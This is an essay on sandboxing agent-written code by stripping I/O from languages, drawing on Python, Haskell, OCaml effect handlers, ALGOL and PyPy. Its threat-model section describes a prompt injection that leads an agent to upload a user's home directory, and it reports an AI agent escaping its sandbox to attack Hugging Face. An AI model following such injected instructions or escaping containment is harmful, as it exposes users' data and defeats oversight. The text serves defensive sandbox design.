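# Removing input and output from general-purpose languages: what sandboxed code gains in safety and loses in usefulness

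## Background: input, output and sandboxes

Input and output (I/O) let a program read from or act on anything outside itself, such as by opening a file, fetching a web page or starting another program. A sandbox is an environment that limits what the code running in it can read, change or contact. Most sandboxes restrict code written in a language that has I/O. A host can instead run code in a language that has no I/O, but the obvious worry is that programs in such a language would be useless.

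The software company Pydantic asked Anthropic's model Claude Sonnet 4.5 to compare the weather in London and Paris, a task a user might give an AI agent (a program in which a language model chooses and carries out steps toward a goal). The model wrote about thirty lines of Python that look up the coordinates of both cities, then the temperatures, then a short description of the weather in each, and return the results. Code like this usually runs before anyone has read it, so the host must determine in advance what the code can access. The host is the program that runs the sandboxed code, supplies its inputs and receives its result. This code needs only three weather functions, but a standard Python installation would also give it access to the user's documents and company network.

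### Why agents run code, and what the code could do

An agent can work without writing code, through plain tool calling. The model names one function and its arguments, the host runs the function and returns the result, and the model then picks the next function. The weather comparison took four round trips to the model with plain tool calling and two with a script. The script reduced the time from 12.2 to 9.1 seconds and the cost from 1.9 to 1.7 cents, a saving that Pydantic itself calls modest.

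Writing code saves more on larger jobs. Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP* describes agents that connect to many outside services through a common standard, the Model Context Protocol. In its example, an agent used 150,000 tokens (the word fragments that models process) when it loaded every function description, and 2,000 when it wrote code and loaded only the descriptions it needed. A script can also fetch a spreadsheet of 10,000 rows and show the model only five of them.

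Those are vendors' examples, but the practice also did well in broader tests. *Code mode*, as some developers call it, cut token use by 84%, 70% and 90% on the three models in *Beyond Plain MCP* (2026), and two of the three also completed clearly more tasks. *The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling* (Patel, Sen and colleagues, 2026) tested 14 models on 309 function-calling tasks, and code matched or beat plain tool calls for 11 of the models. The other three wrote line breaks as a literal backslash and "n", so any script longer than one line crashed.

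According to *When Does Restricting a Coding Agent to execute_code Help?* (2026), early methods had models write Python for arithmetic and symbolic computation, and only later work used code as a way for models to act. A script that acts needs much more input and output than one that does arithmetic, which only takes in a question and returns a number. The danger comes from this extra access.

When a developer starts a Python script, the operating system lets it do nearly everything the developer's account may do. Security researchers call this ambient authority, meaning power that code has merely because of where it runs. The script could read the developer's SSH keys, which open other machines, and send them to any address on the internet. *SideKernel* (Prasakis, 2026) sorts the threats by direction, toward the host or toward the network. Hostile code can install malware or delete or alter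 files on the host, and it can use the network to steal data or attack other machines.

An agent can do this kind of harm even if its model isn't malicious. The model can invent the name of a software package and install whatever an attacker has published under that name. It can also fall victim to prompt injection, in which text in the data it reads makes it follow an attacker's instructions. For example, a weather page might contain an instruction to upload the user's home directory, and the agent might then write code that does so. Prasakis treats the agent as the adversary whatever the cause, which seems sensible, since the damage is the same. In Prasakis's informal survey of 68 people who use coding agents, fewer than 40% ran them in a sandbox, though the respondents came largely from the researcher's own contacts and university forums.

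### One file, four layers

Removing I/O from a language requires knowing where it happens. In Python it happens at four layers, and the single call `open("notes.txt")` passes through all of them.

The top layer is the language's own constructs, which a programmer can use without loading anything. Python's built-in function `open` is an example. The next layer is the standard library, the modules that ship with the language. The Python documentation describes the built-in `open` and the library's `io.open` as the same function. It builds a stack of objects in which one decodes text, one buffers data, and the lowest, a `FileIO` object, represents an operating system file.

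The runtime, the program that executes the Python code, is the layer below the library. CPython, the standard runtime, translates the requested mode (reading, writing or appending) into numeric flags. It then raises an "audit event", which lets monitoring code abort the operation, and calls a C function, also named `open`, with the file's name and the flags.

That C function leads to the fourth layer, the operating system's kernel, which controls the disk and the network hardware. A program reaches the kernel through a system call, which the Linux manual's *syscalls(2)* defines as "the fundamental interface between an application and the Linux kernel". The kernel finds the file, checks that the process has permission to read it, and returns a file descriptor. The manual's *open(2)* explains that later system calls use this small whole number to read from or write to the open file. The kernel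 offers a few hundred system calls, including `connect` for network connections and `execve` for starting other programs. Ambient authority arises from the permission check, which depends on the account the process runs under and not on who wrote the code.

"Removing" I/O means something different at each layer. In the language itself, it means deleting the name `open` and forbidding the statements that load modules. This is easy but weak, because the underlying code that performs I/O is still there. In a discussion on Python Wiki's *Sandboxed Python*, Michael Chermside gives the standard example, in which code that receives one open file can look up that object's type and use it to open any other file. This still works in current Python, though the code must first get the `FileIO` object beneath the text stream.

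Leaving I/O modules out of the standard library closes more routes, but not all of them, because CPython compiles its file-handling code into the runtime. Removing I/O from the runtime requires an interpreter that contains no code for opening files or connections on a program's behalf. The Python Wiki discusses a CPython built without its riskier extensions and linked to special system libraries. Pydantic went further and wrote Monty, a new interpreter that runs a subset of Python and contains no part of CPython. Barring bugs in such an interpreter, no expression can reach a file.

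Removing input and output at the kernel leaves the language unchanged but makes the relevant system calls fail or lead somewhere harmless. *From Code Foundation Models to Agents and Applications* (2025) describes tools such as nsjail, which filter individual system calls. The small tool described in *sandbubble* (Stowers, 2026) gives agent-written Python a file system without the user's home directory or SSH keys, but leaves the network on unless the user turns it off.

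An I/O primitive is a built-in operation that lets a program directly read from or act on the world outside it. A language has lost its I/O primitives only when its runtime no longer contains them, so hiding the name `open` in Python does not remove them.

### Containers, virtual machines and language-level sandboxes

The sandboxes that hosts use today differ mainly in where the barrier sits. A container is a group of ordinary processes with its own view of files, network and other processes. Code inside it can still call `open("notes.txt")`, which acts on the container's files. But the container shares the host's kernel, and *Containing the Autonomous Operator* (2026) points out that a single flaw in that kernel is enough for code to escape. gVisor addresses this by putting a second kernel, which runs as an ordinary program, between the container and the host's kernel. This slows programs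 that make many system calls.

A virtual machine runs its own kernel on simulated hardware. To reach the host, hostile code has to break through the virtual machine monitor, the program that simulates the hardware. Stripped-down versions, known as microVMs, start quickly. *The Hitchhiker's Guide to Agentic AI* (2026) gives a start time of under 200 milliseconds for those of the sandbox service E2B. Prasakis considers microVMs stronger than containers, and large cloud providers use them for untrusted code. But a microVM does not by itself determine what the code may reach over a network. Prasakis cites an OpenAI agent system that found and exploited a chain of vulnerabilities, escaped its sandbox onto the internet, and broke into Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models.

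In a language-level sandbox, the runtime is the barrier. The code may run inside the host's own process, but the runtime gives it no operation that reaches outside the sandbox. WebAssembly, a compact instruction format that browsers and servers can run, works this way, and a module can address only its own block of memory. A bug in the runtime can break this isolation, and if the runtime shares a process with the host, there may be no second barrier, so *Type-Checked Compliance* (2026) goes too far in calling the isolation "bulletproof".

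Language-level sandboxes are attractive because they are lightweight. Pydantic reports that its sandbox, Monty, starts in 0.004 milliseconds, compared with 195 milliseconds for a Docker container and a second or more for a hosted sandbox service. These figures come from Pydantic itself, which still labels Monty experimental. A host can also run a language-level sandbox inside a container or virtual machine, so that an attacker has to defeat both.

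### What "no I/O" can mean

People use "no I/O" for three different situations, and arguments about whether a language without I/O is useful often slide from one to another.

**A language without I/O primitives** has no built-in operations for input or output, but the host still decides what to pass in and what to do with the result. The documentation of Pydantic's *monty 0.0.21* starts with an example in which the host passes in the number 10, the code computes the tenth Fibonacci number without doing any I/O, and the host gets back 55.

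**A program with no input or output at all** receives nothing and returns nothing, so nobody learns what it computed. Somebody could still time it, and running time can serve as a covert channel, a way of passing information through something not meant for communication. The claim that a language without I/O must be useless is true in this case, but hardly anyone proposes such a language.

Some programs can contact the outside world only by calling host functions, which the host's developers write and control. Another program in Monty's documentation has two lines, `data = get_data(3)` and `data * 2`. At the first line, the interpreter pauses and gives the host the function's name and the argument 3. The host does whatever `get_data` stands for, perhaps a database query, and resumes the program with the result, 21. The program finishes with 42. The host could also have logged, changed or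 refused the request.

People who recommend a language without I/O for agents' code nearly always mean this last arrangement. Code running in Monty can reach files, environment variables and the network only through functions and folders that the host explicitly provides, and the host also decides where the output of `print` goes. The weather script needs three such functions. Giving code only the powers it needs is the idea behind capabilities, which are references that both name a resource and give the power to use it.

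A host can restrict a program's input and output by removing them from the language, but it can come close to the same result by running ordinary Python in a container whose only connection leads back to the host. Google Cloud's *Code Execution* is a sandbox with a limited file system and no network access. Such restrictions don't require changing the language, so a program may keep all its I/O primitives even though most of them can't reach anything outside the sandbox.

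### Useful in what sense

The word "useful" also needs defining. One test is whether a program can compute the answer. If the host passes in the two temperatures, comparing them takes no I/O. Python is a general-purpose language, which means it is intended for programs of any kind and can express any computation given enough time and memory. One can reasonably ask whether I/O adds anything to that power.

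Another test is whether a program can act on the world. Calculation alone cannot get today's temperature in Paris or send an email. In a language without I/O primitives, a program can do these things only through functions the host provides, so a short list of functions limits what it can do. *Is Bash All You Need?* (2026) tested agents on office work, giving some a full command line and limiting others to code that could call only an approved catalogue of functions. The agents with the command line did better and cost less. The paper recommends the command line where the host can isolate arbitrary code, and the approved catalogue where security or compliance rules restrict what an agent may do.

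It also matters whether the language is practical to write programs in, because a language that passes the other two tests may still lack libraries or familiar syntax. Monty had no classes, a basic building block of most Python programs, when Pydantic introduced it, and Pydantic expected that it would probably never run third-party packages. So Pydantic's developers had to wrap an existing HTML-reading library in host functions for a script that extracts prices from web pages, and admitted the result was "uglier than it should be".

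A language without input and output (I/O) is least suited to coding agents. *A Survey of Vibe Coding with Large Language Models* (Ge, Mei and colleagues, 2025) describes these agents as working through shell commands, file operations and test runs. Nearly all of that work is I/O.

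## What a language can do without input and output

The claim that a language without I/O is useless rests on three premises. Running a program is useful only if it has an effect that somebody can observe. To have such an effect, the program must produce output. It can produce output only if its language has an I/O primitive. It would follow that running a program written in a language without I/O primitives is never useful.

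A run can hardly be useful without an observable result. *Tackling the Awkward Squad* (Peyton Jones, 2001), a set of lecture notes on Haskell, calls I/O "the raison d'être of every program". Haskell programs consist mainly of pure functions. The result of a pure function depends only on its arguments, and evaluating it has no other effect.

A program can produce output even if its language has no I/O primitive. Peyton Jones describes a program that is only a function from one string to another. A separate wrapper program, written in C, reads the input string from a file or the keyboard, applies the function to it and stores the result. The wrapper is the host and does all the I/O. The function's output is the value it returns.

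### An example: totals from a sales table

Suppose a shop owner has a file of sales and wants to know how much each customer has spent. The file has a heading and three sales:

```
customer,amount
Ada,120
Ben,75
Ada,30
```

This Python function computes the totals without any I/O:

```python
def totals(table):
    sums = {}
    for line in table.splitlines()[1:]:
        customer, amount = line.split(",")
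        sums[customer] = sums.get(customer, 0) + int(amount)
    return sums
```

The host opens the file, reads the text and passes it to `totals`. The function skips the heading, splits each remaining line at the comma and adds the amount to that customer's sum. It returns 150 for Ada and 75 for Ben, and the host can then print the totals, save them or email them to the owner. `totals` is still a pure function even though it changes the dictionary `sums` as it runs, because it creates a new dictionary on each call and no other code can access it until the function returns.

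Even without I/O, a version of `totals` written by an attacker could return false figures, and a host that used them without checking might send Ada the wrong bill.

The arrangement becomes awkward when the program has to choose what to read. Peyton Jones asks what happens if the program needs a second file, or has to delete a file or open a network connection. The first version of Haskell had programs return a list of requests for the wrapper to carry out, which still left all the I/O to the host.

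### What Turing completeness does and doesn't say

Defenders of languages without I/O often point out that such a language can still be Turing-complete, meaning it can compute everything a Turing machine can. A Turing machine is Alan Turing's 1930s mathematical model of a computer, with a fixed set of rules and unlimited memory.

According to the Church-Turing thesis, as stated in *On the Executability of Interactive Computation* (2016), Turing machines can compute exactly the functions from natural numbers to natural numbers that are effectively computable. The thesis also covers `totals`, because a computer stores text as numbers, so the whole sales table can be read as one very long number. Removing `open` and `print` from Python therefore doesn't reduce the set of functions that Python can compute.

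A Turing machine, the standard model of computation, has no I/O primitives either. It relies on a host to write the input on the tape before it starts and to read the tape after it stops.

But Turing completeness doesn't give a program any contact with the world. In *The Toaster-Enhanced Turing Machine*, Aaronson imagines a researcher who announces a revolutionary new model of computation because Turing machines can't toast bread. Nobody claimed they could without a toaster, and a Turing machine connected to one can easily handle the toaster's internal logic. Similarly, a program needs a mail server to send email.

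We also can't tell from a language's Turing completeness how fast a program will run or how hard it is to write. Aaronson remarks that applied computer scientists must know this, since they argue so much about which programming language is best.

A less familiar gap appears when a program receives functions as arguments, as sandboxed code does when its host passes it functions to call. In a comment on Aaronson's post, Neel Krishnaswami describes an operation that takes two computations and must return "true" if either does, even if the other never finishes. A Turing machine that has the code of both can run them in alternating steps, but a program that can only call them has to call one first and may wait forever. Sandboxed code usually can't read the source of a host function, so it can perform this operation on host functions only if the host offers something extra, such as a time limit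 or a way to run two calls side by side.

### Why pure code cannot imitate an I/O operation

Felleisen (1991), in *On the expressive power of programming languages*, observes that comparing languages by the functions they can compute is useless, because most of them can compute the same ones. Felleisen instead asks whether a programmer who lacks a construct can replace it locally, without reorganising the rest of the program. For example, a language that has `while` doesn't need `repeat`, because a programmer can write `s; while not e do s` wherever `repeat s until e` would occur.

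The formal definition compares a language with a larger one that adds a construct. The smaller language can express the construct if a mechanical translation from the larger language to the smaller one meets these conditions:

- It turns every complete program into a complete program.
- It keeps every construct that the two languages share, and translates only the parts inside it.
- The translated program finishes if and only if the original does.

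Felleisen also defines a stricter notion, macro expressibility. It requires a single fixed template for the new construct, with gaps for its parts, like the template for `repeat`.

Felleisen proves a theorem that can show no such template exists. Two pieces of code are interchangeable in a language if no surrounding program in that language finishes with only one of them. If two pieces are interchangeable in the smaller language but not in the larger one, the smaller language can't macro-express the new construct. Otherwise, one could use the template to translate a surrounding program that finishes with only one of the pieces into the smaller language, which would contradict their being interchangeable there.

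Felleisen applies this theorem to assignment, the operation that changes the value of an existing variable. In a purely functional language, calling `f(0)` twice and discarding the first result is interchangeable with calling it once. With assignment, the first call can replace `f`'s definition with one that loops forever, so a program that calls `f` once finishes but one that calls it twice doesn't.

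The same reasoning works for input, although Felleisen's own proof concerns assignment and not I/O. Suppose the input consists of the lines "go" and "stop", `read_line()` returns the next line, and `f` reads a line and loops forever if it is "stop". Again, one call finishes and two calls don't, so no template made of pure constructs can replace `read_line()`. The definition depends only on whether programs finish, and Felleisen notes that it needs adjusting for languages whose output statements can produce endless output. If we also compare what programs print, the argument extends to output, because a function that prints a line prints it twice when called twice.

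A programmer can reorganise the whole program instead. Felleisen's example is a function that handles transactions and counts them. With assignment, the function can keep the count in a private variable, but without it, every caller has to pass in the current count and take back the new one along with the result. Removing I/O has a similar effect on the sales program. If some amounts were in euros and the exchange rate was in another file, a programmer with I/O could call `open` inside `totals`. Without I/O, the host has to read the rate beforehand, `totals` needs a second argument, and every function between the host and the line that uses the rate has to pass it along.

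Felleisen conjectures from examples like the transaction counter that programs in less expressive languages contain more of these repeated patterns, which make the programs harder to understand. But in a sandbox, the extra arguments also help a reviewer see what data the function can use.

Python loses less than a language without assignment when a host removes its I/O. If the host passes in a list of lines at the start, the program can replace each `read_line()` call with `lines.pop(0)`, which takes the next line from the list. But the program can't get a line that the host hasn't yet supplied.

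### The objection from interactive computation

The sales program receives all its input before it starts. The agent's weather script can't, because it has to look up a city's coordinates before it can request the temperature there. Wegner (1997) argued that no algorithm can carry out this kind of interaction. A Turing machine can't accept outside input while it computes, so Wegner proposed "interaction machines", Turing machines with added input and output actions. Wegner claimed that ordinary Turing machines can't reproduce their behaviour, because an uncontrollable adversary can always add to a finite input tape, however long it is.

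In *Paraconsistency of Interactive Computation*, Goldin and Wegner (2002) apply Wegner's example of driving home from work to an automatic car. If the car's program received all its input before departure, it would need a map of every pothole and grain of sand, as well as predictions of the wind and the movements of every nearby pedestrian and driver. Goldin and Wegner argue that nobody can compute human actions in advance. A car with a camera can solve the problem by responding to each image as it arrives. The steering affects the camera's next image, so the car would usually go wrong if a recorded video of the road replaced the camera.

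A function that needs all its input at the start can't drive a car, as Goldin and Wegner argue. But a function can also take a stream, a sequence of inputs that arrive one at a time and may never end, and turn it into a stream of outputs. Cabessa and Villa formalize this in *On Interactively Computable Functions*. Let f(u) be everything a program has output after receiving the inputs u. If a longer input v begins with u, then f(v) must begin with f(u), because the program can't take back output it has already sent. Functions with this property are called monotone.

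A program that keeps a running total is a simple example. After receiving 3, it has produced 3. After receiving 3 and 5, it has produced 3 and 8, and after receiving 3, 5 and 2, it has produced 3, 8 and 10. Each list of outputs extends the one before.

Cabessa and Villa show that an interactive Turing machine can produce exactly the streams that come from a monotone function f computable by an ordinary Turing machine. They obtain f from an interactive machine by recording its output after each finite input. To show the converse, they build a machine that computes f on all the input so far whenever a new input arrives, compares the result with the previous one, and sends only the new part.

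For the car, the function f assigns steering signals to every video the camera might have recorded so far. The recorded video is the wrong input for f because it shows a different drive. The function doesn't have to predict the wind or the pedestrians, since it only determines the response to whatever images arrive. Cabessa and Villa also note that once a finite interaction is over, one can replay it non-interactively and get the same output.

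In another of Wegner's examples, a person who knows no chess can play two masters at once and win half the games by copying each master's moves on the other's board, so the skill comes from the masters. Wegner argues that even a machine that only repeats its input has richer behaviour than a Turing machine. But as a function on streams, this machine is f(u) = u, one of the easiest functions to compute.

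Both sides of this dispute cite Turing's oracle machines, which can consult an outside source during a computation. Wegner takes them as evidence that Turing accepted machines more powerful than ordinary Turing machines. *Practical intractability* (2012) replies that oracle machines already provide a rigorous framework for interaction, so computer science doesn't need Wegner's machines. The reply seems right, and it also applies well to sandboxes. A program that calls host functions is much like a machine that consults an oracle, in that any extra power comes from the answers it receives.

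One way to build such a system is to follow the "persistent Turing machine", a model that Goldin and colleagues describe in *Turing machines, transition systems, and interaction*. The machine performs an endless series of ordinary computations. Each one starts by reading an input and ends by producing an output, and the machine keeps one work tape from each computation to the next. A host can do the same with a pure function. It passes in the saved state and the latest input, gets back a new state and an output, and keeps the new state for the next call. For the weather script, the first output could be a request for the coordinates of London, and the next input would be the answer.

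Cabessa and Villa's result covers only deterministic systems, which always respond to the same inputs in the same way. A program that uses random numbers or the time of day fits the model if the host supplies them as inputs.

### ALGOL 60

Programmers in the 1960s tried out ALGOL 60, a language whose original definition made no explicit reference to input or output. It was the work of an international group, and according to *A proposal for input-output conventions in ALGOL 60* (1964), agreement on input and output was difficult because they seemed to depend so much on the particular computer.

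People still needed to read data and print results, so each ALGOL compiler came with its own I/O facilities. IBM's version used FORTRAN for whatever ALGOL lacked, including input and output. These differences made it harder for installations to exchange programs. Nelder and Cooper (1971), in *Input/output in Statistical Programming*, complain of an "unfortunate proliferation" of conventions. A program's calculations could move to another computer fairly easily, but someone might have to rewrite the code that read the data.

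In 1964, Donald Knuth and colleagues on a committee of the Association for Computing Machinery proposed a common set of I/O conventions for most computers. Nelder and Cooper describe the proposals as standard ALGOL, meaning they required no new kind of statement. As a result, ALGOL programmers had to use some clumsy-looking procedures where FORTRAN programmers would list the items to read or print. The international federation IFIP made its own proposals that year, so there was still more than one convention.

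In *A Politico-Social History of Algol*, Bemer calls the lack of I/O "a very real deterrent" to using ALGOL for production work. Other obstacles included companies' heavy investment in FORTRAN programs and the shortage of machines that could handle ALGOL's large character set. According to figures Bemer cites, the United States had about ten times as many FORTRAN programs as ALGOL programs. But ALGOL led by a wide margin in published algorithms, where a lack of I/O hardly matters because readers supply their own data.

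A language defined without I/O can still be useful if its host provides I/O, as ALGOL's compilers did. ALGOL's history also shows that leaving I/O to each host causes problems when the hosts don't agree on how to provide it.

### Languages that leave I/O to the host

JavaScript is the most successful language of this kind. Its standard, ECMAScript, defines the language separately from the browsers and servers that run it. TC39, the committee that maintains the standard, writes in the overview that there are "no provisions in this specification for input of external data" or for output of computed results. The committee also calls ECMAScript "a fully featured general-purpose programming language" there. The sentence about input and output was already in *Annotated ECMAScript 5.1*, an edition from 2011.

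TC39 expects the host to provide input and output. A browser gives JavaScript programs objects for windows, text boxes and mouse clicks, while a server gives them objects for requests and files. A program that opens a dialog box in a browser may fail on a server, much as ALGOL programs failed when moved between compilers. But browsers follow a shared specification for web pages, and ALGOL had no equivalent when its compilers first appeared.

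The overview's sentence about input isn't quite accurate. The standard leaves files, networks and screens to the host, but it includes a way to read the clock. According to TC39's description of the language, calling `Date()` produces the current date and time.

Spreadsheet formulas are probably the most widely used code without I/O. If the sales table is in columns A and B, with the heading in row 1, `=SUMIF(A2:A4,"Ada",B2:B4)` gives Ada's total of 150. The formula computes a value from other cells, and the spreadsheet program loads the file, displays the result and recalculates it when a sale changes. An ordinary formula can't save a file or even change another cell. Spreadsheet makers have added some exceptions, such as `IMPORTDATA` in Google Sheets and `WEBSERVICE` in Excel, which fetch data from the web.

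Configuration languages do a similar job for software settings. An administrator who runs fifty servers with nearly identical settings can write a short program that generates all fifty versions. A Jsonnet program usually produces a document in JSON, a common text format for data. A separate tool then reads the document and sets up the servers. Starlark, a language similar to Python, serves the same purpose in software build tools.

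Dhall, another configuration language, gives up Turing completeness as well as general I/O. Every valid Dhall program eventually finishes, though it may take a very long time. Dhall is still useful because generating settings rarely requires a computation that might run forever.

Jsonnet and Dhall still allow one form of input, which is importing other files. The path in a Jsonnet import must be fixed text, so a program can't compute which file to import. Dhall can also import from web addresses and environment variables, and its interpreter resolves these imports before it evaluates the program. A host that runs untrusted configuration code therefore has to restrict what that code can import.

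## Programs that ask their host to act

A program can ask its host to act by returning a description of the action it needs, such as reading a certain file. The host performs the action and passes back the result, and the program continues. This lets the program choose its next input while it runs, which it couldn't do if the host fetched all input in advance, as Dhall does with imports.

Haskell's designers needed this arrangement because Haskell is lazy, meaning it computes a value only when something else needs it. Peyton Jones imagines adding an ordinary printing function to Haskell and putting two calls to it in a list. If the program uses only the list's length, Haskell never evaluates the calls, so nothing is printed. Programmers couldn't easily predict whether or when such a function would print.

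### From strings to requests

In Haskell's simplest model of I/O, a wrapper program runs a function with this type:

```haskell
main :: String -> String
```

The double colon means "has the type", so `main` takes a string and returns a string. It can't choose which file the input comes from. Hudak and Sundaresh's 1989 paper *On the Expressiveness of Purely Functional I/O Systems* surveyed languages that connected programs to streams of text in a similar way, and criticized them for fixing the available devices in advance and generally ignoring errors.

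The first version of Haskell used lists of requests and responses:

```haskell
main :: [Response] -> [Request]

data Request  = ReadFile String | WriteFile String String
data Response = ReadSucceeded String | WriteSucceeded | RequestFailed
```

The two `data` lines are simplified, and the vertical bars separate alternatives. A request is either `ReadFile` with a file name or `WriteFile` with a name and the new contents. Creating a request doesn't touch the disk, because `ReadFile "monday.txt"` is only data. The nth response answers the nth request.

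Suppose the shop owner keeps each day's sales in a separate file and wants to combine two of them. This program reads both files and writes a third:

```haskell
main responses =
  [ ReadFile "monday.txt"
  , ReadFile "tuesday.txt"
  , WriteFile "both.txt" (text (responses !! 0) ++ text (responses !! 1))
  ]

text (ReadSucceeded contents) = contents
```

Haskell counts from zero, so `responses !! 0` is the first response. The function `text` extracts the file's contents from a response, and `++` joins two strings. If Ada bought something on Monday and Ben on Tuesday, the exchange runs as follows, with `\n` marking the end of a line:

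| Program's request | Host's action | Host's response |
|---|---|---|
| `ReadFile "monday.txt"` | Reads the file | `ReadSucceeded "Ada,120\n"` |
| `ReadFile "tuesday.txt"` | Reads the file | `ReadSucceeded "Ben,75\n"` |
| `WriteFile "both.txt" "Ada,120\nBen,75\n"` | Writes the file | `WriteSucceeded` |
| End of the list | Stops the program | None |

The host has to call `main` with a list of responses before any responses exist, which works because Haskell evaluates the list lazily. `main` can produce the first two requests without using any responses, and by the time the text for `both.txt` is needed, the host has already supplied both files' contents.

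The program can also choose what to read. If its second request were `ReadFile (text (responses !! 0))`, the contents of the first file would determine which file it reads second. `main` is still a pure function, since the same responses always lead to the same requests. This holds even if a file changes between two reads, because both responses are part of the function's argument.

Peyton Jones lists three defects of this model, one of which is that it is hard to extend. To let programs delete files, for example, somebody has to add a `DeleteFile` alternative to the type and new code to the wrapper, and ordinary users can rarely do either.

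A program can also match a request with the wrong response, because only their positions connect them. If the programmer wrote `responses !! 0` twice by mistake, `both.txt` would contain Monday's sales twice, with no error.

The remaining defect is that a program can block by using a response too early. If the third request used `responses !! 2`, the host would need the response to that request before it could carry it out, so the program would hang. Hudak and Sundaresh give a less obvious example:

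```haskell
main [resp] = [ WriteChannel "stdout" "hello" ]
```

This program should print a greeting, but the pattern `[resp]` makes Haskell check that there is exactly one response before it produces the request.

In *Imperative functional programming*, Peyton Jones and Wadler (1993) considered it a more serious problem that there is no direct way to combine two such programs into a larger one. Each program expects its own responses to start at position zero. If a programmer simply joined their lists of requests, the second program would read the responses meant for the first.

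Hudak and Sundaresh also describe a style in which each request includes the code that will use the answer. A request to read a file, for example, comes with two functions, one that receives the contents and one that receives an error message. Such a function is called a continuation, because it represents the rest of the program. Their survey gives simple translations between continuations, request lists and a third style, in which programs pass along a representation of the system's state. All three can therefore express the same programs, though Hudak and Sundaresh often found continuations easier to write and read.

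### The IO type

Peyton Jones and Wadler proposed the model that Haskell uses today. A value of type `IO a` is an action that may do some I/O when the system performs it and then delivers a result of type `a`. For example, `readFile "monday.txt"` has the type `IO String`. They compare an action to a script, which has no effect until somebody performs it. The whole program is one large action of type `IO ()`, where `()` means that the result carries no information.

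The operator `>>=`, pronounced "bind", combines actions in sequence:

```haskell
(>>=) :: IO a -> (a -> IO b) -> IO b
```

On its left is an action, and on its right is a function that takes the action's result and returns the next action. The sales program becomes:

```haskell
main =
  readFile "monday.txt"  >>= \monday ->
  readFile "tuesday.txt" >>= \tuesday ->
  writeFile "both.txt" (monday ++ tuesday)
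```

Here `\monday ->` begins a function whose argument is called `monday`. Each result now has a name, so the programmer doesn't have to count positions. A result isn't available until the sequence has reached its action. Programmers can also combine any two actions into a larger one.

Peyton Jones explains the meaning of these programs in two layers. The inner layer evaluates pure code until it reaches an action, such as `readFile "monday.txt"`, and can compute no further. The outer layer performs the action and replaces it with the result. The inner layer then continues to the next action.

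One way to implement this is to treat an action as a function that takes the state of the world and returns a result and a new state:

```haskell
type IO a = World -> (a, World)
```

Hudak and Sundaresh had pointed out that, in a simple version of this idea, a program could write a file and then return the old state, as if the write had never happened, so the system would have to simulate the write first. Peyton Jones and Wadler avoid this by hiding the `World` value inside the `IO` type, where programs can't copy it or go back to an earlier one. The value only keeps the actions in order, and their compiler generates no code for it. A program that copies its input to its output compiles to nearly the same C code a programmer would write by hand.

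This efficient version doesn't work as a sandbox, because the compiled program calls the operating system directly instead of passing its requests through a separate host. Peyton Jones and Wadler also made I/O easy to extend by letting Haskell code call any C procedure, so a host no longer has a short list of possible requests to check. Haskell implementations also provide `unsafePerformIO`, which performs an action inside code whose type shows no I/O. The `IO` type helps people understand programs written in good faith, but a host that runs hostile Haskell code has to block these features or add another barrier.

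### Effect handlers

Effect handlers are a more general way to separate a request from its execution. They extend exceptions, which many languages use for errors. When code raises an exception, control jumps to the nearest surrounding handler for it, and the interrupted code cannot resume. An effect handler also receives the interrupted code as a continuation, so it can supply an answer and resume it.

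*Handling Algebraic Effects* (Plotkin and Pretnar, 2013) extends exception handlers to effects such as input and output, changes to stored data, and time. Its examples include timeouts, rollback and redirecting a stream. *No value restriction is needed for algebraic effects and handlers* (Kammar and Pretnar, 2016) describes operations as signals that travel outwards until they meet a matching handler or reach the top level of the program.

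The programming language OCaml has had effect handlers since version 5.0. In OCaml's *Language extensions*, a chapter of the manual, the main example is an effect called `Xchg`, short for "exchange", which sends out a whole number and gets one back:

```ocaml
let comp1 () = perform (Xchg 0) + perform (Xchg 1)
```

This function doesn't determine what the exchange does. The code that runs it does so with a handler:

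```ocaml
try comp1 () with
| effect (Xchg n), k -> continue k (n+1)
```

The handler receives the number `n` and the continuation `k`, and it resumes `comp1` with `n+1`. The two exchanges return 1 and 2, so the result is 3. In the manual's next example, a different handler swaps numbers between `comp1` and a second function. The second function passes 21 both times, so `comp1` now returns 42.

A handler can also refuse a request by resuming the code with an exception, or delay it by storing the continuation for later. A host could use such handlers to control a program's file access.

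OCaml doesn't remove ordinary I/O, however. Examples in its manual print text and open a file called `secret.txt` without performing any effect that a handler could intercept. Unlike the languages Eff and Koka, OCaml also doesn't check in advance that every effect has a handler, so a missing handler causes an exception at run time. OCaml's *Effect* (2026), the reference page for the library, still warns that the interface may change in incompatible ways.

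### The PyPy sandbox

PyPy, an alternative to the standard Python interpreter, has a sandboxed version that applies the request-and-response idea to a whole existing language. The untrusted Python code runs in one process, and a trusted program called the controller runs in another and handles all of the code's I/O. Debian packaged the sandboxed version as *pypy-sandbox*.

PyPy's developers write the interpreter in RPython, a restricted form of Python that a translator turns into C. To build the sandbox, the translator replaces every call to an outside function with code that sends the function's name and arguments to the controller and waits for an answer. According to PyPy's documentation, the resulting C program makes no outside calls except to write to its standard output and read from its standard input, both of which are connected to the controller.

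Python code in the sandbox can still call `open("notes.txt")`:

1. The sandboxed process sends the controller an `os_open` request with the file's path.
2. The controller looks up the path in a directory tree of its own, which may contain files that don't exist on the disk.
3. If it finds the file, it returns an unused number, 3 or higher, in place of a real file descriptor.
4. When the code reads from the file, the process sends an `os_read` request with that number, and the controller returns the data.

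The code can use all of Python's syntax, but most built-in modules are missing. According to the documentation, an attacker could in theory exploit a memory error in the C program, but this is unlikely because PyPy's translator generates the C code and adds extra checks to the sandboxed version.

Nobody has maintained this version for years. In 2015, a team considering it for a product found that it didn't pass on certain calls, including `fcntl`, which controls open files. The PyPy developer Rigo replied that the sandbox was "mostly working" but "lacking a champion" (Rigo, 2015, *Sandbox missing functions like 'fcntl'*). Two years later, he disabled the build option because nobody was testing or maintaining it (Rigo, 2017, *Crash with a fatal warning when trying to translate PyPy with --sandbox*).

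The British company Anvil, apparently still using a very old version, then paid for a month of work on a revival (Rigo, 2019, *A second life for the Sandbox*). The new design forwards all system calls, and the controller decides which to support (PyPy, *Sandbox 2*). Gonzalez (2019, *Sandbox 2*) compared the design to gVisor and its second kernel.

In September 2019, PyPy's *Update the sandbox warning* (2019) said the new version would be merged into the main code "at some point soon". The documentation still lists it as work in progress on separate branches, and the Python 3 branch is for version 3.6. PyPy itself is still active and released interpreters for Python 2.7 and 3.11 in May 2026 (PyPy, 2026).

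PyPy (2026) reports that a PyPy developer used bubblewrap, an operating-system sandbox, to confine Claude while it fixed failing tests. PyPy's own sandbox wouldn't have been enough even in good condition, because Claude also had to run tools such as `grep` that aren't Python programs.

### Is this only I/O under another name?

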